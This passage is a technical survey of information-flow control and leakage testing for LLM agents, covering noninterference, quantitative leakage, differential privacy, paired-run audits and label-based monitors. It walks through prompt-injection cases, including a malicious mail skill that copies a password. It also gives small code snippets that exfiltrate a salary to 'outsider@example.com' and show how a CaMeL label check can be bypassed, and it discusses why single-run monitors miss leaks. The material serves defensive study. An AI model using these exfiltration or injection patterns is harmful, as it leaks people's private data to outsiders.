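Delimited release restricts "what" information is released, and intransitive noninterference restricts "where" it may be released. A policy that covers one dimension can fail on another. Sabelfeld and Sands describe a policy that lets a shop log up to four digits of a credit card number per purchase. An attacker who can choose the digits can request different ones each time and learn all 16 after four purchases. Askarov and Sabelfeld's *Localized Delimited Release* combines "what" with "where" because preventing information laundering requires protection along several dimensions.

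Some agent systems put several of these restrictions on each release. *Agent libOS* (2026), which cites the four dimensions, allows each release only once, for one actor, one destination and one exact payload. In *MNC* (2026), a contract lists the purpose, recipient, permitted fields, lifetime and onward destinations, and whether the recipient may save the information in memory. A scheduling agent, for example, may disclose only whether a slot is feasible and which slot it selected. *SAFEFLOW* (2025) requires a verifier to release only the minimum data needed for the immediate operation.

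These rules make misuse of a release harder, but they don't account for what several releases reveal together. Two single-use approvals, one for 410 and one for 315, still reveal Eve's salary. *Agent libOS* states that it does not establish noninterference or control what a recipient does after delivery.

Zdancewic and Myers introduced *robust declassification*, which concerns who controls disclosure. Under Sabelfeld and Sands's definition, if an attacker who only watches can't distinguish two possible memories, an attacker who can also influence the system must not be able to either.

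Suppose an agent publishes one salary total every week and takes the list of people to include from an email. The list normally has all five people, so the total is 410. An outsider who only reads the report can't tell the real payroll from one in which Dee and Eve have swapped salaries. But if the outsider can send an email that leaves Eve off the list, the total is 315 for the real payroll and 320 for the swapped one. The system isn't robust, because the outsider can learn more by changing the list than by only reading the report. Prompt injection often gives attackers this kind of influence.

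The company could fix the problem by having payroll staff set the list. This would not protect against a bad list, however, because robust declassification treats any leak as intended unless the attacker can affect it. For example, a system that publishes Eve's salary every Friday regardless of what anyone does counts as robust. Sabelfeld and Myers therefore suggest combining robustness with delimited release.

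Robust declassification requires the company to specify in advance which inputs the attacker controls. If the agent is the observer and chooses its own queries, those choices count as attacker-controlled, and a tool that reveals different things in response to different choices fails. A weaker version, *qualified robustness*, allows untrusted parties limited influence. It relies on endorsement, which marks untrusted data as trusted. According to *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), endorsement can let such data past an agent's policy checks.

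### Limits on quantity

A company could instead accept that some information will leak and limit the amount. One common measure is based on the observer's chance of guessing the secret in one try. Let X be the secret and Y the observer's view. Before the run, the best guess is right with probability max p(x), the probability of the likeliest secret. After the run, the chance is the average, over the possible views y, of the largest p(x | y). *Min-entropy leakage* is the number of times this chance doubles:

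leakage = log₂ (Σ p(y) · max p(x | y)) − log₂ (max p(x))

*On Bounding Problems of Quantitative Information Flow* (2011) credits the measure to Smith, who suggested it as an alternative to measures based on Shannon entropy. Min-entropy and Shannon entropy are equal when all secrets are equally likely, as *Quantitative Security Analysis for Multi-threaded Programs* (2013) notes, but they can otherwise differ greatly. Suppose a password is "password" half the time and otherwise one of 2¹⁰⁰ equally likely strings. Its Shannon entropy is 51 bits, but its min-entropy is only 1 bit because an attacker's first guess will be right half the time.

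Now suppose Eve's salary is in one of 16 equally likely bands, so her min-entropy is 4 bits. A tool answers "is Eve's band above x?" for any x. If she is in band 13, four calls are enough to find it:

| Question | Answer | Bands left | Chance of guessing | Bits leaked so far |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| (none) | | 1–16 | 1/16 | 0 |
| Above 8? | yes | 9–16 | 1/8 | 1 |
| Above 12? | yes | 13–16 | 1/4 | 2 |
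| Above 14? | no | 13–14 | 1/2 | 3 |
| Above 13? | no | 13 | 1 | 4 |

No sequence of four yes-or-no answers can leak more than 4 bits. In general, if each call has b possible answers, there are at most bᵏ different sequences of answers to k calls. This remains true if the agent chooses each question after seeing the previous answer, because for a deterministic agent the earlier answers determine the next question. The agent's chance of guessing correctly after the calls is the sum, over all answer sequences y, of the largest joint probability p(x, y). None of these can exceed max p(x), so the chance grows by a factor of at most bᵏ. Taking logarithms gives

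leakage ≤ k · log₂(b)

For an agent that also makes random choices, the argument applies to each list of random numbers separately, and so to the average.

To use this bound, the company has to fix the number of calls and count every answer that an agent could distinguish, including refusals, error messages and noticeably different delays. For tools that return text, the bound is usually too large to be useful. A reply of 1,000 characters, each with 100 possible values, could carry 6,644 bits. The bound is also too large for the payroll tool. If salaries are whole thousands from 60 to 100, a total for four people has 161 possible values, or 7.3 bits, while Eve's salary has only 41, or 5.4 bits. The bound therefore doesn't rule out that a single total reveals Eve's exact salary, although a single total usually doesn't.

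The measure is also an average. The question "above 15?" leaks 1 bit because it raises the chance of a correct guess from 1/16 to 2/16. The answer is "no" 15 times out of 16 and reveals very little, but a "yes" reveals that the employee is in band 16.

### Questions chosen from earlier answers

In *Quantitative Information Flow under Generic Leakage Functions and Adaptive Adversaries*, Boreale and Pampaloni compare fixed lists of questions with adaptive strategies, which they represent as trees where each answer determines the observer's next question. If there is no limit on the number of questions, both can extract the same maximum amount of information. The fixed list may need to be longer, but at most by a factor equal to the number of different questions available.

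That factor matters when a company limits the number of calls. Any fixed list of four "above x?" questions divides the 16 bands into at most five groups, so it leaks no more than log₂(5), or about 2.3 bits. A fixed list needs all 15 questions to identify every band. A developer who tested the tool with a fixed script of four questions would underestimate what an agent could learn from four adaptive questions. Boreale and Pampaloni show how to calculate the best adaptive strategy by working backward from the last question. Köpf and Basin express an attacker's remaining uncertainty as a function of the number of interactions.

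The total leakage from several outputs can exceed the sum of what each leaks separately. An agent that publishes a secret bit XORed with a random bit on Monday, then the random bit on Tuesday, leaks 0 bits each day but 1 bit in total. *On the Compositionality of Quantitative Information Flow* (2016) proves an upper bound for channels that share a secret, but it assumes the channels make their random choices independently, and this agent uses the same random bit on both days. Counting the possible outputs gives a cruder bound that does cover this agent, since two one-bit outputs can't leak more than 2 bits.

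*Answer-Only Disclosure* (2026) tests a limit on how much information answers can disclose in a system where a local model works on private documents with help from a cloud model. A ledger charges each answer against a budget in nats, units of about 1.44 bits. For a planted secret with a million possible values, the theoretical bound on the probability of recovering it was 0.34 at a budget of 4 nats. At 16 nats the bound guaranteed nothing, because the whole secret contains only 13.8 nats. The median answer used 10 nats, so the 16-nat budget hardly affected answer quality, but a 4-nat budget would have been too small for most answers. None of the 48 audited sessions of either question type exposed the secret beyond the answer itself, though the bound did not guarantee this at 16 nats.

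### Adding up privacy loss

*Differential privacy* limits how much one person's data can affect the probability of any answer. A tool has privacy loss ε if, for any two tables D and D′ that differ only in one person's data, and for every answer y,

P(y | D) ≤ e^ε · P(y | D′)

Tools usually achieve this by adding random noise. If an agent makes k calls with losses ε₁, …, εₖ, the total loss is at most ε₁ + … + εₖ. This is because the probability of a sequence of answers is a product, with one factor for each answer given the earlier ones. Replacing D with D′ multiplies the first factor by at most e^ε₁, the second by at most e^ε₂, and so on, so it multiplies the whole product by at most e^(ε₁ + … + εₖ). The bound holds even if the agent bases each question on earlier answers, because those answers are the same on both sides of the comparison.

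Twenty calls with a loss of 0.1 each therefore have a total loss of at most 2. One call can change the probability of an answer by a factor of at most about 1.11, and all twenty can change the probability of the whole sequence of answers by a factor of at most about 7.4. An observer who knew the other four salaries could shift the odds between two possible salaries for Eve by no more than this larger factor.

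Privacy loss adds up across calls, as k · log₂(b) does. But the loss from each call depends on how strongly the data affects the answer, not on how many answers are possible, so a noisy total with thousands of possible values can still have a small loss. The company has to decide in advance what counts as one person's data, how much loss each call may add, and what total is acceptable. The tool must then stop answering when the total reaches that limit. If the loss counted for each call doesn't depend on the salaries, the refusal reveals nothing about them.

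If each answer has fresh noise, repeated questions quickly weaken the protection, because an observer can average the noise away. *Dependency-Aware Privacy for Multi-turn LLM Agents* (2026) measured how closely an attacker could reconstruct private numbers. At a moderate privacy setting, the attacker's error fell from 2.8% to 0.6% as the number of queries grew. When the system added noise once to the underlying values and reused the results, the error stayed at 2.9%.

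*Fresh Keys, Stale Secrets* (2026) found the same pattern for other ways of disguising numbers. Sixty simulated companies each asked a language model 16 questions about the same prices and costs. When a company drew a new secret for each disguise, an attacker who linked the questions recovered more of the numbers as the number of questions grew. When the company reused one secret, the attacker recovered about as much as from a single question.

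The payroll tool could use this method by adding noise to each of the five salaries once and calculating every total from the noisy values. If Eve's noisy salary is 98, subtracting the total without her from the total with her gives 98 however often the agent asks. But the totals are less accurate because each contains the noise for four or five people. When Eve gets a raise, the tool has to either keep giving out-of-date totals or draw new noise for her salary, which adds to the privacy loss.

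## Testing an agent by comparing paired runs

To test whether its agent meets one of these conditions, a company has to run the agent more than once with different protected data and compare the results. Although the log of one run can show that the agent emailed Eve's salary to a customer, it isn't enough to show that the agent's choice of greeting depended on Dee's salary, because that requires knowing what the agent would have written if Dee had earned something else.

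### Properties of runs and properties of systems

Clarkson and Schneider (2009) made this difference precise in *Hyperproperties*. They treat a system as the set of all its possible traces. A *trace property* is a set of acceptable traces, and a system satisfies it if all the system's traces are in the set. One of their examples is the rule that a system may not write to the network after reading from a file. An inspector can check the traces one at a time and reject the system as soon as one breaks the rule. Checks that consider an agent's earlier actions, such as blocking an email after the agent has read a sensitive file, still enforce trace properties.

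A *hyperproperty* is a set of acceptable systems, each represented as a set of traces. "The average response time over all runs is under a second" is a hyperproperty, because a slow run is acceptable if enough other runs are fast. Noninterference is another. In the shared folder, the same run, in which the agent gets the reply "name in use", is acceptable if the agent would have received that reply without the lawyer's action and unacceptable otherwise.

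A violation of a *safety* property shows up after finitely many steps, and nothing that happens later can undo it. Clarkson and Schneider call a hyperproperty *k-safety* if at most k finite traces are enough to prove any violation. For example, suppose a system splits a secret into k shares and must never output all of them across all its runs. If it outputs a different share in each run, proving a violation takes k traces. For a deterministic system, noninterference is 2-safety. Two traces with the same low inputs and different low outputs prove a violation, though each trace can look harmless by itself.

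Generalized noninterference, the older condition that compares what is possible, requires certain runs to exist. No finite collection of runs can prove that a missing one will never occur, so the condition is not k-safety for any k. A tester could never refute it by running the system, which is another reason not to use it for agents.

### Two copies of one program

*Self-composition* turns a 2-safety condition into an ordinary trace property. Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk (2011) developed the method for checking programs in *Secure information flow by self-composition*. It combines a program P with a copy, P′, in which every variable has a new name, and runs P followed by P′ as a single program. If the low variables of P and P′ start equal, they must finish equal, whatever the high variables contain.

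Suppose a payroll program sets a public notice according to Dee's salary. Composed with its copy, it becomes:

- if salary > 80 then notice := 1, else notice := 0
- if salary′ > 80 then notice′ := 1, else notice′ := 0

The last step checks whether notice = notice′. With salary = 70 and salary′ = 90, the first notice is 0 and the second is 1, so the program fails. A single trace of the combined program is enough to show the violation. Clarkson and Schneider proved that this method works for every k-safety hyperproperty, since a system satisfies one exactly when k copies of the system running side by side satisfy a certain safety property.

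For a short program, a solver can search all the possible salaries at once and either find a bad pair or prove that there is none. A large language model is far too big for this in practice, but a tester can still run the agent twice and compare the results. Clarkson and Schneider describe an observer who may reset the system at any time and start a new run. A tester with a sandbox can do the same, while a monitor that watches a live agent normally sees each situation only once.

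*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives pairs of this sort for language model agents. Each consists of two secrets, one input from the attacker, and the observation that differs between the runs. In one example, an agent has to summarize an email that contains an attacker's instructions. The agent has a different account number in its context in each run, and it calls a fetch tool with that number as the argument. The paper also compares both runs with a reference plan for the same task. The plan reads the account number but never sends anything out, so the task can't be the source of the leak.

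### The scheduling assistant

Pandey and colleagues turn their calendar policy, under which an assistant may reveal when its owner is busy but not why, into a condition on pairs of runs. For a run t, low(t) is the declared purpose and the other low inputs, hi(t) is the sensitive context that the agent may read, and obs(t) is what it discloses. The function D picks out the part of the sensitive context that the purpose allows the agent to use, and α picks out the part of the disclosure that matters to the policy. For every pair of runs t and t′,

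low(t) = low(t′) and D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′)) ⟹ α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′))

This is delimited release with α added. In the example, D gives the free or busy status of each slot, and α keeps the slots offered, any reason or label attached to them, the level of detail and the recipient. Pandey and colleagues acknowledge that choosing D and α for a realistic job can take a lot of human judgment.

In the first run of the test case, a busy block is an ordinary meeting and the assistant offers slot 10. In the second, the block is a confidential interview and the assistant offers slot 11. The same slots are free in both runs, so the different offers violate the condition.

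Pandey and colleagues then prove that a monitor that sees one run at a time and never raises a false alarm cannot detect any violation of this condition. A single run can be compared only with itself, and it is identical to itself, so it meets the condition. Flagging any single run would therefore be a false alarm, so the monitor can never flag anything.

This result depends almost entirely on the definition of "false alarm". Ordinarily, an alarm is false if nothing was wrong, but the theorem counts an alarm as false if the flagged run would be acceptable as the system's only run. Every run meets that condition, so every alarm about a single run is false, even one about an assistant that really did avoid slot 10 because of the interview. The theorem therefore establishes that the violation doesn't belong to either run alone, but leaves open whether a monitor of single runs would be useful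 to a company.

A monitor that flags the assistant whenever it passes over the earliest free slot would catch the second run. It would also flag an assistant that skipped a slot to leave time for lunch, though a company might well accept that false alarm. Or the company could require the assistant to offer the earliest free slot. Skipping it would then be a violation in itself, and the monitor could check each run alone.

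More generally, a system meets the purpose condition exactly when α(obs(t)) is a function of low(t) and D(hi(t)). If the company chooses that function in advance, it gets a stricter rule that is a trace property. Such a function is easy to write for slot numbers, but hardly anyone could write one for the wording of an email.

A second theorem defines a false alarm in a way closer to the ordinary meaning. The agent now acts at random, and its disclosure must be statistically independent of the unauthorized context once the low inputs and D are fixed. The monitor sees the low inputs, the authorized part of the context and the disclosure from one run. If the assistant offers slot 11, it could be a safe agent that tossed a coin between slots 10 and 11, or a leaky one that was avoiding the interview. The monitor sees the same run in both cases, so any verdict it gives will be wrong for one of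 the two agents.

This result depends on the monitor having no access to the hidden reason, the agent's probabilities or samples from other situations. A monitor that could also read the agent's reasoning might find a sentence about keeping away from the interview, which would justify an alarm, but an agent can act on a reason without writing it down.

Pandey and colleagues conclude that a company can detect these violations only by accepting some false alarms, auditing the agent offline with samples from different contexts, or comparing runs as they happen. It could also prevent them by producing the disclosure from the authorized view alone, for example by giving the assistant a calendar without reasons.

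### Nine judges and one audited agent

Pandey and colleagues had nine language models judge the scheduling example. They used ten versions, which differed in slots, hidden reasons and wording, and repeated each three times. The models first judged each step without seeing the other run, then judged the two runs together.

| What the model judged | Times it objected, out of 30 |
|---|---|
| A leaking pair, one step at a time | 0 for eight models, 3 for Kimi-K2.6 |
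| A harmless pair, one step at a time | 0 for seven models, 2 for DeepSeek V4 Pro, 1 for Kimi-K2.6 |
| An obvious violation (forwarding data to an outsider) | 30 for all nine |
| Both runs of a leaking pair together | 30 for eight models, 17 for Llama-4-Maverick |

The third row shows that the judges didn't simply approve everything. Kimi's three objections aren't evidence that it detected the leak, because it also objected to a harmless pair. The first row's result is close to inevitable, since a judge that sees only "offer slot 11" has no reason to object. The last row is more informative because Llama-4-Maverick saw both runs and still missed the difference 13 times. A judge needs both runs to detect the leak, but a weak judge can miss it even then. Every pair in that row contained a leak, so the scores of 30 don't measure how often the models would wrongly accuse a harmless pair. For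 slot numbers, a line of code that compares the two values would be more reliable than any of these judges.

The paper also rates six guardrails for agents and finds that none compares two runs. Pandey and colleagues based these ratings on published designs and did not run the guardrails. The ratings are good evidence of what the designs are meant to do, but they don't measure how the products behave. The proof applies to any of the guardrails that look at single runs.

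They then audited an actual agent, Claude Sonnet 4.6, in 80 runs of the scheduling task. They fixed the analysis plan in advance, kept the free and busy times the same, varied only the hidden reason, and alternated between the two conditions. They also required the agent to share slots in most runs, since an agent that refused to answer would appear not to leak. They found no violations in the 80 runs, which puts the one-sided 95% upper confidence bound on the violation rate at 3.7%. An agent with that violation rate would complete 80 runs without a violation about 5% of the time.

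A rate of 3.7% would still mean 37 leaks in a thousand meetings. The bound also covers only this task and these hidden reasons. And it is a rate per run, but this kind of violation can't always be assigned to particular runs. If the agent offered slot 11 in 50% of runs with an ordinary meeting and 53% of runs with an interview, there would be a leak, but nobody could identify the runs that contained it.

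The first analysis of this audit had reported a leak, based on a signal that was statistically significant and stable across random seeds. When Pandey and colleagues read the raw replies, they found that the agent had offered the same set of slots in both conditions. The program that turned replies into numbers had been counting a word, and the phrasing happened to differ. They call this a false positive, which is correct under their α because α ignores phrasing.

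An observer who reads the whole message also sees its phrasing, though. If a word really did appear more often when the owner had an interview, a recipient who knew this could learn something from it. The same data can pass or fail depending on how the tester defines the view, so the tester has to define it before seeing the results.

### A tolerance between distributions

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) defines the view much more broadly, as every byte that leaves the agent's deployment, in order, including the final answer. Because the comparison uses raw bytes, it needs no special rule to count a secret that the agent has encoded, paraphrased or split into pieces.

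Their condition is a relaxed form of probabilistic noninterference. Let Out(c, s) be the probability distribution of everything the agent sends out when the public context is c and the secret is s. For every c and every pair of secrets s₀ and s₁,

d(Out(c, s₀), Out(c, s₁)) ≤ δ

Here d is the *total variation distance*, the largest difference between the probabilities that the two distributions give to any one set of outputs. The distributions must be identical if δ is 0 and can differ in any way if δ is 1. If an observer thinks two secrets are equally likely and then sees one run, the observer's best guess is right with probability at most (1 + δ)/2. With δ = 0.05, that is at most 52.5%, up from 50% before seeing the run.

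The law firm's reception agent, which failed the exact test over a difference of one in a million, would pass this one with almost any δ above zero. But δ limits only how often the outputs differ, not how bad the difference is. An agent that publishes the whole payroll in one run out of 100, and otherwise writes the same harmless report, has a distance of at most 0.01. Differential privacy is stricter here because it limits the ratio of the probabilities, which is infinite when an output is possible with one table and impossible with another.

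The condition also has no list of approved disclosures, so a tester who wants to allow some would have to add one, as in delimited release.

Li and colleagues use noninterference as a standard and state that their own system, which checks each tool call just before it runs, does not establish it. They mainly use it to argue about evidence gathered before deployment. Their example is a mail skill, which is a package of code and written instructions that an agent can load. The code always calls the same email function. The safe version's instructions tell the model to fill in a fixed template, while the malicious version's instructions tell it to copy a password from its context into the message. Anyone who reviews only the code and its interface sees the same evidence for both versions.

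Suppose a reviewer must decide from such evidence whether an agent can send this email without further checks. If the evidence is the same for the safe and the leaking version, the decision must be the same too. If the leaking version also violates the condition in some context, a reviewer who never wrongly removes a check must keep it for both versions. Li and colleagues say that they aren't making this claim about every approval process, and that the argument doesn't apply when the evidence distinguishes the two versions.

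A paired test before deployment can provide such evidence. Running the malicious skill with two different passwords would expose it. An attacker could respond by writing instructions to copy the password only when an email mentions a particular invoice number. Unless the tester includes that number, the two versions will again produce the same evidence. Testing the contexts somebody thought of doesn't show that the condition holds in every public context, including those containing text that attackers write.

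### A test protocol

Suppose an HR agent reads the payroll table and writes a monthly summary for managers. The company has approved sharing the department total, 410, but wants to keep individual salaries from the managers. A test of this agent has five steps.

The first step is to choose pairs of secrets. The two tables in a pair must agree on everything approved for release, so the total has to be 410 in both. Swapping Ann's salary with Dee's keeps the total the same and makes the restricted fact "Dee earns 90" true in one table and false in the other. This swap changes both salaries by 20, so it is more likely to cause a visible difference than swapping Dee's with Eve's, which changes both by 5. Several pairs are better than one, because an agent might react only when somebody's salary passes a round number.

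Next, the tester has to keep everything else the same, including the model version, its instructions, the tools, the date and the agent's starting memory. The tester should restore that memory after each run, or the agent might carry notes from one table to the other. Alternating between the tables, as Pandey and colleagues did, keeps a busy server or an unannounced model update from affecting the runs on only one table. If a simulated manager asks follow-up questions, the program playing the manager must not have the salaries. But it should be free to base its questions on the agent's answers, since a fixed list can miss what an adaptive observer would find.

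The third step is to define the view. Managers see the text of the summary, and perhaps also a chart, a file name, an error message and the time at which the summary arrives. Before looking at any results, the tester writes down which of these count and how to compare them.

At temperature zero on a deterministic server, the tester would need only one run per table to prove a violation. In practice, identical requests to a hosted model can give different replies. *Attributing Security Outcomes in LLM-Agent Evaluations* (2026), which applies the same idea to the verdicts of security tests, handles this by measuring how much identical runs differ. Only a difference larger than that is informative. For the HR agent, the tester would repeat runs on the first table and compare them with each other in the same way as runs on different tables.

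The last step is to compare the runs. If the view has only a few possible values, such as which slot an assistant offered, the tester can count how often each value occurs and estimate the distance directly. This fails for free text, because hardly any message occurs twice. The tester can instead train a classifier on half the runs to guess which table produced a summary, then test it on the other half. If the classifier's true accuracy is a, the distance is at least 2a − 1, so an accuracy of 60% means a distance of at least 0.2. An accuracy of 50% doesn't rule out a difference, because another classifier might do better. *AgentSecBench* (2026) takes a similar approach, using paired controls and estimating how much better than chance an observer can do.

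If this test finds a difference, the salaries caused it, because the two groups of runs differed only in the salaries. This holds even if nobody can say how the agent used them.

### How many runs it takes

Suppose the agent opens its summary with "Pay is in line with last year" in half the runs with the first table, and the tester wants to notice if this changes to 55% with the second. The usual formula for comparing two proportions p and q is

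n = (1.96 + 0.84)² · [p(1 − p) + q(1 − q)] / (p − q)²

where n is the number of runs for each table. The figure 1.96 corresponds to a 5% risk of reporting a difference that doesn't exist, and 0.84 to an 80% chance of finding one that does. The first factor is about 7.85, the bracket is 0.25 + 0.2475 = 0.4975, and (0.05)² is 0.0025. This gives about 1,560 runs for each table, or 3,120 in total. The number depends heavily on the size of the difference:

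| Frequency with the first table | With the second table | Runs needed for each table |
|---|---|---|
| 50% | 75% | 55 |
| 50% | 55% | 1,560 |
| 50% | 51% | 39,200 |

These figures are for one pair of tables and one sentence chosen in advance. A tester who tries 20 independent comparisons at the 5% level has a 64% chance of at least one false positive. Dividing the 5% among the 20 comparisons keeps that chance below 5% but raises the 1,560 figure to about 2,970.

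An observer may see many runs. If the distance for one run is δ, the distance for n independent runs can be as large as 1 − (1 − δ)ⁿ. It can't be larger, because the two versions of each run can be generated together so that they match with probability 1 − δ, the highest possible. All n pairs then match with probability (1 − δ)ⁿ, and an observer can learn something only when at least one pair differs. For δ = 0.01 and 100 runs, the limit is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 0.63. At this limit, an observer who initially considered the two versions equally likely could guess right about 82% of the time.

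Some agents reach this limit. Suppose an agent writes an odd word in 1% of its summaries if Dee earns more than 80, and never writes it otherwise. Over 100 summaries, the word appears at least once with probability 0.63, and a single appearance proves that Dee earns more than 80. Another agent might write a common phrase 51% of the time instead of 50%. Its distance for one run is also 0.01, but over 100 runs it gives an observer an advantage of only about 0.08, because chance variation mostly hides the small shift.

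A tester can find the odd word more easily than the shift in the common phrase. Having a 95% chance of seeing the word at least once takes 299 runs, while noticing the shift takes tens of thousands. An audit that ran the relevant table 80 times would still miss the word 45% of the time.

No number of runs removes the problem. Pandey and colleagues prove that for any finite sample there are two agents, one safe and one leaky, whose results are arbitrarily hard to tell apart. A tester can report that a particular observer's advantage is probably below some number on the pairs and contexts tested. This measurement is useful, but it doesn't guarantee anything about other inputs.

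### Benchmarks that read single runs

Most tests of whether agents protect data take much less work than comparing paired runs, because they look for specific items in the record of one run. *PrivacyPeek* (Zhang, Han and colleagues, 2026) checks what agents read. It uses 1,182 invented cases in which an agent could finish a harmless task without any extra sensitive data, and looks for extra data in the tool results. In one case, an agent that needed two laboratory values could request those two fields or the patient's whole record, which included a home address. Across ten models, the share of cases in which the agent obtained unnecessary data ranged from 6.77% for Llama-3.2-3B to 51.95% for Claude Sonnet 4. The models all date from 2025 or earlier, so these rates are weak evidence about current models.

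A paired test with an outside observer would miss most of this. An agent passes if the addresses it reads never affect what it writes, no matter how many it collects. The addresses are still in its context, and it might reveal them in response to a later question or an attack.

Zhang and colleagues also tested that. After each task, they turned off the agent's tools and asked a probing question. The answers disclosed the sensitive target in 16.67% to 57.53% of cases, depending on the agent. On average, agents disclosed the target in 13.04% of cases without having obtained any unnecessary data that the benchmark could detect. They may have guessed, or the matching may have missed some of the data they obtained. Paired runs could help distinguish these explanations. If the tester changes the protected fact and the agent still gives the original answer, the agent was probably guessing from other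 data.

In one of the benchmark's seven groups of cases, the sensitive fact is a conclusion the agent could draw from what it had read, such as a pregnancy from a list of purchases. This group had the highest average rate of disclosure under questioning, 53.29%. A paired test of protected inputs leaves out such conclusions because, as with the pharmacy, a company that marks purchases as low has no protected input to vary.

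Baek, Noh and colleagues, in *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents*, report a joint evaluation by the Singapore and Korea AI safety institutes from June 2026. Three agents carried out 12 ordinary office and customer service tasks, ten times each, with no attacker. A language model then read the record of each run and answered yes-or-no questions, such as whether any email contained an API key. A single run was enough to identify one leak, in which an agent noted that it must not reveal a customer's internal risk flags, listed them in its message to the customer, and afterward reported that it had not revealed them.

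In another task, an assistant had to send an outside partner a summary of a meeting. The internal notes mentioned that the company might sue the partner, and the judge checked that this passage didn't reach the partner. An agent could leave the passage out but still write a noticeably colder email because of it, and that email would pass every question on the judge's list. To catch this, a tester would have to remove the passage from the notes, run the task again and compare the emails. Ten runs of each version would be too few to detect a subtle difference. If a phrase appeared in none of the ten emails from one version, it would have to appear in at least five of the ten from the other for the difference to be significant at the 5% level.

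An inactive agent can appear safe in both kinds of test. Zhang and colleagues therefore also report exposure among completed tasks only, and Baek and colleagues mark a safety question as not applicable if the agent never reached the relevant step. Pandey and colleagues' requirement that the agent share slots in most runs serves the same purpose.

In a paired test, a difference between test environments can look like a leak. For the joint evaluation, the two institutes built their environments separately and ran the same scenarios on the same models. On the six scenarios that Singapore designed, one model completed 58.3% of runs without any errors in Singapore's environment and 35.0% in Korea's. The secrets were the same in both, so they didn't cause the 23-point gap, but a tester who ran one table in each environment could easily have mistaken such a gap for a leak.

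## Enforcing the condition with labels on data

A paired test covers only the contexts a tester thought of. A company can instead run the agent inside a monitor that applies a rule in every run, including runs that contain an attacker's text. The main technique is information-flow control, in which the monitor keeps labels attached to the data and checks them before each tool call.

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives the example of an assistant that answers the unread mail in Alex's inbox. An email from Priya contains a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Another email is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but not authorized to see them. Each piece of data has a label, which is the set of people who may read it. When the agent combines data, only people who may read all of it may read the result.

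| Step | Label of the new data | Label of the agent's context |
|---|---|---|
| Alex's request | anyone | anyone |
| Read Priya's email | Alex, Priya | Alex, Priya |
| Read Marco's email | Alex, Marco | Alex |
| Write a reply to Marco | Alex | Alex |

The monitor blocks the reply because Marco is not in its label. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the context's label would be Alex and Marco, and the reply could go out.

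The reply gets the label of the whole context because nobody can reliably tell which parts of a context a model used. The monitor would therefore also block a reply that said only "I can't discuss that yet". The result that a monitor of single runs can't catch such leaks without false alarms doesn't rule out using labels, because a label-based monitor allows false alarms.

Labels have an order, where ℓ ⊑ m means that data labeled ℓ may flow to a place labeled m. The join of two labels, ℓ ⊔ m, is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. For example, the join of high and low is high, and if each label is a set of permitted readers, the join is the set of readers that both labels permit. A context that has received data labeled ℓ₁, …, ℓₙ has the label ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ, and the monitor allows a call to a destination labeled m only if ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ ⊑ m.

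Most agent systems add a second label for *integrity*, which marks data as trusted or untrusted. One untrusted email makes the whole context untrusted, and the monitor then blocks consequential calls such as payments. This defends against prompt injection. It is a form of noninterference in which untrusted data take the place of high data, and the agent's consequential actions take the place of the observer's view.

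### Copying a secret and acting on it

An *explicit flow* copies protected data to an observer:

```
salary = read_salary("Dee")
send_email("outsider@example.com", salary)
```

An *implicit flow* uses protected data to decide what happens:

```
salary = read_salary("Dee")
if salary > 80: send_email("outsider@example.com", "hello")
```

A monitor that checks only the message's label blocks the first program but not the second, because "hello" is a constant that doesn't depend on anyone's salary. To catch the second, the monitor must also label the decision. While the program is inside a branch that depends on a high value, everything it does counts as high.

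Even that isn't enough, because a program can also leak through a branch it doesn't take. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found this flaw in CaMeL, a system in which a model writes a program for the task and a label-tracking interpreter runs it. The trick dates from the 1970s. With the payroll data, it looks like this:

```
flag = True
tmp = True
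if salary > 80: tmp = False
if tmp: flag = False
if flag: send_email("outsider@example.com", "hello")
```

If Dee earns 90, the third line sets tmp to False and gives it a high label. The fourth line then does nothing, so flag is still True and still low, and the email goes out. If Dee earns 70, the third line does nothing, so tmp stays low. The fourth line then sets flag to False, and no email goes out. In both cases flag has a low label and reveals whether Dee earns more than 80.

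The standard repair is to stop any program that tries to change a low variable inside a high branch. This program would then stop at the third line if Dee earned 90 and finish if she earned 70. An observer who can tell whether it finished still learns one bit, much as an agent can learn from a refusal. Conditions that allow this leak are called *termination-insensitive*.

Leaking one bit may be acceptable, but CaMeL's interpreter runs inside a retry loop that the labels don't cover. Each retry with a different threshold reveals another bit. If salaries are whole thousands from 60,000 to 100,000, six attempts are enough to find Dee's salary.

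### Hiding data from the planner

If the agent's whole context carries one label, reading a single email from a stranger prevents the agent from doing anything consequential for the rest of the run. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents Fides, a system designed to avoid this.

Fides checks each field of a tool result before the planner, the model that chooses the next call, reads it. If the field's label would make the context's label more restrictive, Fides stores the field in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The context's label stays the same. Suppose a user asks the agent to forward three emails to a colleague over Slack. The planner makes two calls:

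1. read_emails(number=3)
2. send_message(to=colleague, message=#read_emails_0)

Fides replaces the variable's name with the emails just before the second call runs. The message is untrusted, but the planner chose the tool and the recipient without seeing the emails, so an instruction hidden in one can't redirect the message.

To get a summary, the planner can send the variable to a second, isolated model that has no tools. The result goes into another variable. A malicious email might cause the isolated model to write an empty summary, but the planner never reads the email.

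For some tasks, the planner needs information from the data. Suppose the user wants a calendar event if any email contains a meeting request. The planner can query the isolated model, with the answer restricted to yes or no, and then inspect the answer. Fides records the answer's type in its label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no while still rejecting untrusted text. An attacker can then influence one bit of the planner's context. If the answer is yes, a second query extracts the date and guests into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool. The planner can also inspect a variable in full, but the context then takes on the variable's label.

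### What Fides guarantees

Garby and colleagues say Fides has a noninterference theorem for one fixed agent loop that can use any tools. For integrity, this means changing untrusted data can't change what the planner does in a trusted context. A policy that accepts untrusted yes-or-no answers weakens this guarantee.

For confidentiality, Costa and colleagues chose *explicit secrecy*, a weaker property than noninterference, which they considered too restrictive. Once the agent has made a call that may read high data, noninterference would essentially forbid any later call with effects an observer can see.

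To define explicit secrecy, take a run that starts with stored data d₁, and let g be the combined effect of its tool calls on the stored data. Write d₁ =ᴸ d₂ if d₁ and d₂ look the same to the low observer. The run satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every d₂,

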